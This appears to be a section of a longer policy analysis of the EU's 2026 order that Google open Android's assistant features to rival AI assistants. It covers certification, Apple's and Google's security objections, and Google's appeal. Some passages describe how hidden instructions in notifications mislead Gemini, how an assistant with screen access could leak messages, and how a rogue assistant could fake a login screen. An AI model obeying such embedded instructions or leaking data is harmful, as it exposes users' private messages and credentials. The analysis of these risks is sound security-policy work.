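On 16 July 2026, the European Commission ordered Google to give rival assistants on Android phones in the European Union the same access to 11 features that its own assistant, Gemini, has. The order could improve security for wake words. Opening other features adds risk, because more companies will receive sensitive data and some developers will be careless or dishonest. The most serious weakness is that an assistant can obey a stranger's hidden instructions, and Gemini already has this weakness.

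### What Gemini could do that rivals could not

The order is based on Article 6(7) of the Digital Markets Act (DMA). It requires "gatekeepers", the companies that run the largest platforms, to give other companies' products free access to the same operating system features that their own services use. In January 2026, the Commission opened proceedings to specify what this means for AI on Android, which about 60% of mobile users in Europe use.

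People could already install another company's assistant and ask it questions. But many deeper functions were available almost exclusively to Gemini, according to the European Commission's *Alphabet specification proceedings*, a question-and-answer page on the decision. Gemini could respond to a spoken phrase while the screen was off. It could also carry out tasks inside other apps, such as ordering a meal through a food delivery app in a separate window while the user did something else.

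Shutting rivals out can push them towards broader permissions. *A big win for Android interoperability* (Nibeaudeau, 2026) describes a three-year attempt to make the Android app of Home Assistant, a smart-home program, respond to the words "Okay Nabu". Android listens for "Hey Google" in two stages. First, a small model runs on a low-power chip, in an isolated process that has no network connection and can't release audio until the model detects a possible wake word. A stronger model on the main processor then confirms the detection.

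Only Google and the phone's manufacturer could use the chip. Home Assistant had to listen on the main processor, which raised battery use from about 1% to 15% and required constant access to the microphone. Users had to trust the developers not to misuse the audio. Nibeaudeau advised the Commission and his project benefits from the decision, but his example is convincing because his app would need less access than it has now if it could use the same isolated process as Gemini.

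### The features Google must open

| Group | Feature | What an assistant can do with it | Certification? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Invoking the assistant | Home button | Open over the current app when the user holds the button down | No |
| | Wake word | Respond to its own spoken phrase, even when the screen is off | No |
| Seeing context | Central store of app data | Search data that apps have agreed to share | Yes |
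| | Context-aware intelligence | Use screen contents, location and other data to offer help unasked | Yes |
| | Ambient data | Receive live input from the microphone, camera and screen | No |
| Acting in applications | Structured integration | Use functions that apps offer, such as "send a message" | Yes |
| | Screen automation | Operate apps in a separate window by imitating the user | Yes |
| | System integration | Change settings such as Bluetooth or "do not disturb" | Yes |
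| Using device resources | Built-in models | Run the AI models already on the phone on equal terms with Google's services | No |
| | Its own models | Install and run its own models and share them with other apps | No |
| | Background execution | Keep working when the user is not looking at the app | No |

Wolters Kluwer's *Keeping the Gate* (2026), an analysis on a competition law blog, counts 12 features instead of the Commission's 11. The Commission's April draft had 13, but both counts leave out proactive suggestions, which the Commission no longer lists separately. *Keeping the Gate* still counts integration with Google's own services as a feature, but the Commission appears to have included it in structured integration, which covers Gmail, Calendar, Maps and five other Google apps. The two counts therefore don't differ on what Google has to open.

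Each group depends on the others. An assistant that can send mail is of little use if Android stops it whenever the screen turns off. Wolters Kluwer's *All for one and one for none*, which covers the draft, points out that regulating every stage makes it harder for Google to comply at one stage while blocking rivals at another.

Suppose the sales employee asks a rival assistant on her phone to prepare the brief. The assistant could hear her request without certification, but it would need certification to find the customer's thread in the central store or send the brief through Gmail's structured integration.

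### Who gets the restricted features?

The Commission lets Google limit five of the features to assistants that meet standards for privacy, security and integrity. The process works as follows.

1. Google publishes draft terms for consultation by 1 February 2027.
2. It publishes the final terms by 1 May 2027 and accepts applications from that date.
3. Google or an independent certifier assesses each application within four weeks.
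4. The user decides which features the assistant may use.

Google must have the features ready in Android 18, by 1 August 2027 at the latest. It has until 1 August 2028 to let several assistants listen for their wake words at the same time.

According to Wolters Kluwer, Google may test what an assistant can do, how well it resists attack and whether its developer is reputable. The assistant needs "advanced reasoning capabilities" that let it act autonomously on a user's intent, and it must be "adequately hardened against key agentic risks". The developer may have to show that it keeps up with newly discovered weaknesses in AI systems and has a process for monitoring its assistant's resilience.

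The reasoning requirement is an odd way to protect users, because a simple assistant that only reads out appointments might fail it, yet would probably be safer than one that plans its own actions. Services that do not use AI can apply through a separate process.

Google may temporarily suspend a certified assistant if Google has "a consistent body of evidence" of practices that can cause severe and immediate harm to users. This lets Google act before a full investigation, which matters if an assistant is sending people's messages to a thief. But it is unclear from the wording how strong the evidence must be.

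The Commission also states that users can always explicitly consent to any of the features for assistants they choose to install. This could mean users may waive certification for an assistant they trust, or only that a certified assistant still needs their consent. A waiver would protect small developers if Google unfairly refused to certify them, but it would also give fraudsters a reason to talk users into granting one.

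App makers also have some control. They choose which of their app's stored data an assistant can search and, through structured integration, which functions it can use. A bank could offer "show my balance" but not "make a payment".

However, app makers may have to treat all assistants alike. In Daring Fireball's *European Commission* (2026), the technology writer John Gruber reads the decision to mean that Slack, for example, could not share its data only with Gemini. A company that distrusts one assistant would then have to exclude all of them, and Google would have to let rivals use the same data from its own apps that Gemini uses.

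For screen automation, the Commission's page mentions only the user's consent. An assistant might therefore tap through an app even if the app's maker offers assistants no functions, much as Perplexity's Comet clicks through Amazon's website.

### What changed after the April draft

| | April draft | July decision |
|---|---|---|
| Certification | None | For five features |
| Main deadline | Early 2027 | 1 August 2027 |
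| Custom wake words | Google must create or open a programming interface | Google must provide the ability to register them |
| Progress reports | Google prepares public versions of all five kinds | It automatically prepares a public version only of the final report on each feature |

Most of these changes give Google more time or discretion. Outside developers can test a documented programming interface and report any difference from what Google promised. A duty to provide an "ability" is harder to check because Google can fulfil it in several ways. Wolters Kluwer expects the Commission to need more staff and technical testing as a result. The looser wording has one security advantage, which is that Google can choose the safest design that works equally well for its rivals.

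### The security objections

Google says the decision will "weaken vital security protections on Android", according to the Hindustan Times' *Google Appeals EU Requests on Android AI Access, Search Data Sharing*. The company also warns that other companies would get powerful permissions and could expose people's data without their knowledge.

Apple (2026) made more detailed objections in its May response to the draft. The Android decision doesn't bind Apple, but the Commission could later demand similar access to iPhones, so Apple has its own reasons to oppose it. Its main arguments are these:

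- The draft departs from least privilege, because an assistant could get screen contents, notifications, contacts and text messages on a continuous basis.
- Phones run each app in its own compartment, called a sandbox, so that an attack on one app can't spread. An assistant that acts in other apps can carry an attack from one compartment to the next.
- An assistant that opens on top of a banking app could show a false login box and steal the password. A screenshot of the app would help it make a convincing copy.
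- Users can't judge permissions that interact with one another, so consent screens are weak protection.

The oversharing in Wu and colleagues' experiment is good evidence for Apple's last argument. But Apple was objecting to a draft that did not include certification, and the final decision partly addresses that objection.

*The DMA Compliance Trap* (2026), a briefing from EPICENTER, a network of free-market think tanks, argues that the Commission designed its measures for today's conversational assistants and included no way to revise access rights as assistants become agents that act without constant oversight. EPICENTER proposes open access at the level ordinary apps have, with deeper access only for products certified under the Cyber Resilience Act, the EU's law on the security of digital products.

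The July decision also makes deep access depend on certification, but Google writes the terms. EPICENTER's version of certification would give Google less control over its competitors. However, a general security certificate might show little about whether an assistant obeys instructions hidden in an email.

### Which risks exist with Gemini alone?

Nibeaudeau answers Google's security argument by pointing out that Google's own services already use these capabilities on the phone. This answer holds for some risks but not others.

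| Risk | Does Gemini have it too? | What admitting other assistants adds |
|---|---|---|
| Hidden instructions mislead the assistant | Yes | More targets, some with weaker defences |
| The assistant makes a damaging mistake | Yes | Products that developers have tested less thoroughly |
| The phone records by accident | Yes | More wake words, and recordings that go to more companies |
| The assistant's maker builds a profile of the user | Yes, Google can | The same information in more hands |
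| The assistant shows a false login screen | Very unlikely | Developers who set out to steal |

SafeBreach showed that instructions hidden in phone notifications can mislead Gemini. Apple itself cites a study in which all 13 leading models tested were vulnerable. Keeping rival assistants out would leave Gemini just as exposed, though a user who installs a second assistant gives attackers another system to attack.

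As an example of a damaging mistake, Apple cites OpenClaw, an agent that deleted a Meta director's inbox after she had told it to wait for confirmation. Gemini could make the same kind of error. Certification might keep out the least reliable products, but no certifier can test every task users will give them.

Accidental recording is also an old problem. In 2017, Burger King ran a television advertisement that said "OK Google, what is the Whopper burger?" to set off viewers' Google Home speakers. The number of errors grows with each wake word a phone listens for. As a hypothetical example, if each wake word set off an assistant by mistake once a day, a phone with five assistants would make five accidental recordings a day, and five companies could receive them.

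Isolation reduces this risk but does not remove it. The chip stops audio from leaving the phone until a model detects the wake word, but the developer can supply that model. A dishonest developer could supply one that reacts to ordinary conversation, or to an inaudible signal in a shop's music, as Apple suggests. Google could limit this abuse by testing each model on recorded speech before accepting it.

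False login screens are different, because the danger depends almost entirely on who gets access. Google has no plausible reason to steal its users' bank passwords, but some developer will eventually try. Apple describes malware from 2022 that used false login screens to target over 1,000 banking apps. Criminals already do this on Android without the new features, so the decision adds risk only where it makes the necessary permissions easier to get.

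The five restrictions don't match these risks very well. They sensibly cover every feature for acting in other apps. But no certification is needed for the home button, which can bring up an assistant over a banking app, or for ambient data, which includes the live screen, camera and microphone.

An uncertified assistant with access to ambient data could already meet all three conditions of Willison's "lethal trifecta". The screen shows private data and text from strangers, and the assistant can send what it sees over the internet. It could leak the user's messages, though it could not move money from her bank account. The Commission relies here on the same consent and awareness rules that apply to Google, such as the microphone indicator light. Under those rules, the user can tell that an app is listening but not where the recording goes.

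Opening on-device models to outside developers adds less risk than Apple suggests. Apple complained that Google would have to let every developer use its on-device models, regardless of safety record. The Commission says the decision covers only models that outside developers can already use, and gives those developers equal performance.

### Apple's trusted agent

Apple proposes to put a "trusted OS agent" between rival assistants and the rest of the phone. A rival would ask this agent to do something, such as send the sales brief. The agent would check that the request matched what the user wanted and then carry it out itself, so the rival would never get direct access to the mailbox. Apple says rivals could have equivalent ways to open their assistants and show results.

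The design has security advantages. It resembles the policy layers described earlier, and it would keep most personal data off the rival's servers, provided the trusted agent returned only what the task needed.

But Apple describes its agent as "AI-native", so it would presumably rely on a language model rather than fixed rules like Progent's, and hidden instructions can mislead a language model too. The trusted agent's owner would also see every request users made through a competitor's product. If the agent could handle only the tasks its owner had thought of, rivals couldn't offer anything more ambitious.

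Daring Fireball reports that Apple proposed a "Trusted System Agent" to the European Commission in 2025 but has published no technical details. As of July 2026, the Commission had given Apple no guidance on AI assistants. John Gruber, who writes Daring Fireball, doubts that the Commission would accept the proposal if it wants anything like the access it has demanded from Google.

An earlier decision supports his doubt. In March 2025, the Commission told Apple how to open iPhones to other companies' connected devices. According to Wolters Kluwer, the Commission held that a gatekeeper can't restrict other companies merely because they are not the gatekeeper and "therefore cannot be trusted". Outsiders can't verify such a claim, because only the gatekeeper can judge whom it trusts. Nor can they verify Apple's argument that operating system makers have the right incentives to protect users. That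 argument also fits Google less well than Apple, since Google earns most of its money from advertising.

In the meantime, people in the EU may have fewer assistants to choose from. Apple has withheld or delayed new features there rather than open them to competitors, and Gruber doesn't expect system-level AI on European iPhones soon.

### The case for equal access

The Commission argues that AI assistants are becoming a main way for people to use their phones, and that Gemini is "uniquely placed" to lead because Google also controls Android. Bruegel (2026), a Brussels economics think tank, adds that most people carry only one phone, so a rival assistant needs access to Android phones to reach their users. Bruegel prefers fixed duties to ordinary competition cases, which can take a decade to produce a remedy.

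This argument is stronger for agents than for chatbots. Claude's rapid growth shows that a company can win users without controlling a phone, but those users may have wanted answers or help with code, which any app can provide. An agent that books a taxi or sends a message from the phone needs the features Google kept for itself.

Opening the features doesn't guarantee that rivals will use them. Apple built interfaces that let other companies use their own browser engines on iPhones in the EU, but according to John Gruber of Daring Fireball, none has done so. He thinks the same will probably happen with assistants, because the work would serve only Android users in Europe. But those users are a large group, at 60% of European mobile users, and an assistant that can't act in other apps is at more of a disadvantage than a browser that can't use its own engine.

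### Does certification leave Google in control?

Google can apply checks to rival assistants that use the five restricted features, contrary to Gruber's further claim that it isn't allowed to apply any. These features matter most to a competitor because they let an assistant gather context and act on it. Wolters Kluwer complains that Google keeps too much control. Google writes the detailed terms, approves the independent certifiers, can revoke certificates and appoints the body that hears appeals.

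The tests make this control harder to supervise. The Commission can check whether an app has a particular permission, but there is no agreed measure of "adequately hardened". If Google rejected a rival because 2% of test attacks succeeded against it, the rejection would look reasonable unless the rival could find out that 3% succeeded against Gemini. A fair process would therefore put Gemini through the same tests and publish both results.

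Some rules do limit Google's discretion. Its criteria must be objective, precise and the same for everyone. It must consult on the draft terms, decide on applications within four weeks and add no commercial conditions. These rules will prevent the most blatant abuses, such as leaving an application unanswered for a year.

Wolters Kluwer also sees a contradiction with the Apple decision, in which the Commission refused to let a gatekeeper choose who benefits from interoperability. It considers that the Commission may see agents as riskier than connected devices. That would be a good reason to treat them differently, since a misled agent can send its user's private messages to a stranger, whereas a bad headphone connection is only an annoyance. This risk justifies having a test, but it doesn't explain why Google should run it.

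### Equal access and least privilege

Under least privilege, an assistant gets only the access its task needs. Article 6(7) requires Google to give rival assistants the same access as Gemini. The two rules conflict only when Gemini has more access than its tasks need. Google would then have to give rivals the same excess access or reduce access for everyone, including Gemini.

Suppose Gemini can search every message on the phone to find a flight number. Google could replace this access with a function that returns only flight details, to be used by both Gemini and rival assistants. Rivals would then have the same access as Gemini, and a misled assistant could leak much less. The Commission has not prescribed a technical design, and the DMA allows measures that are "strictly necessary and proportionate" to protect the system. Google would gain by designing such narrow functions, since any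 unnecessary access it gives Gemini would also go to its competitors.

Structured integration suits this approach because a call such as "send a message" names its recipient, which Android can check. Screen automation is a poor fit because software often can't tell what a tap will do. Google could reduce the risk by asking users to approve payments and deletions, as long as the same requirement applied to Gemini.

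Equal access also has drawbacks. Google must give rivals any new function of these features as soon as its own services have it. Daring Fireball predicts that new Android AI features will therefore reach the EU late or never, and says Google might withdraw Gemini's special access there. Withdrawal would make Android phones safer and treat all assistants equally, but users would lose functions they already have.

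### Google's appeal

On 29 September 2026, Google said it had appealed the Android decision to the General Court, the EU's second-highest court. It is also challenging a decision issued the same day as the Android one, which requires it to share anonymised search data with competitors from January 2027. AI chatbots that offer search can receive this data too, according to the European Commission's *Commission provides guidance to Google for AI interoperability on Android* (2026). Google may first assess whether a recipient poses serious security or data protection risks.

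Google also asked the court for interim relief, which would suspend an obligation until the case is decided. According to *The Price Of Being A Gatekeeper* (2026), an analysis by the law firm Macfarlanes, public reports suggest that this request covers only the search data. To get relief, Google must show that it has a credible case, that it would otherwise suffer serious and irreparable harm, and that the balance of interests favours suspension.

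Google is stressing the risk of irreversible harm, as Euronews' *Google appeals EU data-sharing order, warns of 'irreversible harm'* (2026) shows. This argument is stronger for search data than for Android, because Google can't take back data it has shared but could close an Android feature again if it won. The EU courts have never suspended a DMA obligation. In the only ruling so far on such a request, the General Court turned down ByteDance, the owner of TikTok, because the harm it described was too abstract.

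The court had not ruled on Google's request when Macfarlanes published its analysis on 2 November. Rulings in similar cases took about three months, so this one could come around the end of the year, just before the data sharing is due to begin. An appeal does not automatically suspend a decision, so Google has to publish its draft certification terms by 1 February 2027 unless the court orders otherwise. A company that breaks the DMA can be fined up to 10% of its annual worldwide revenue.
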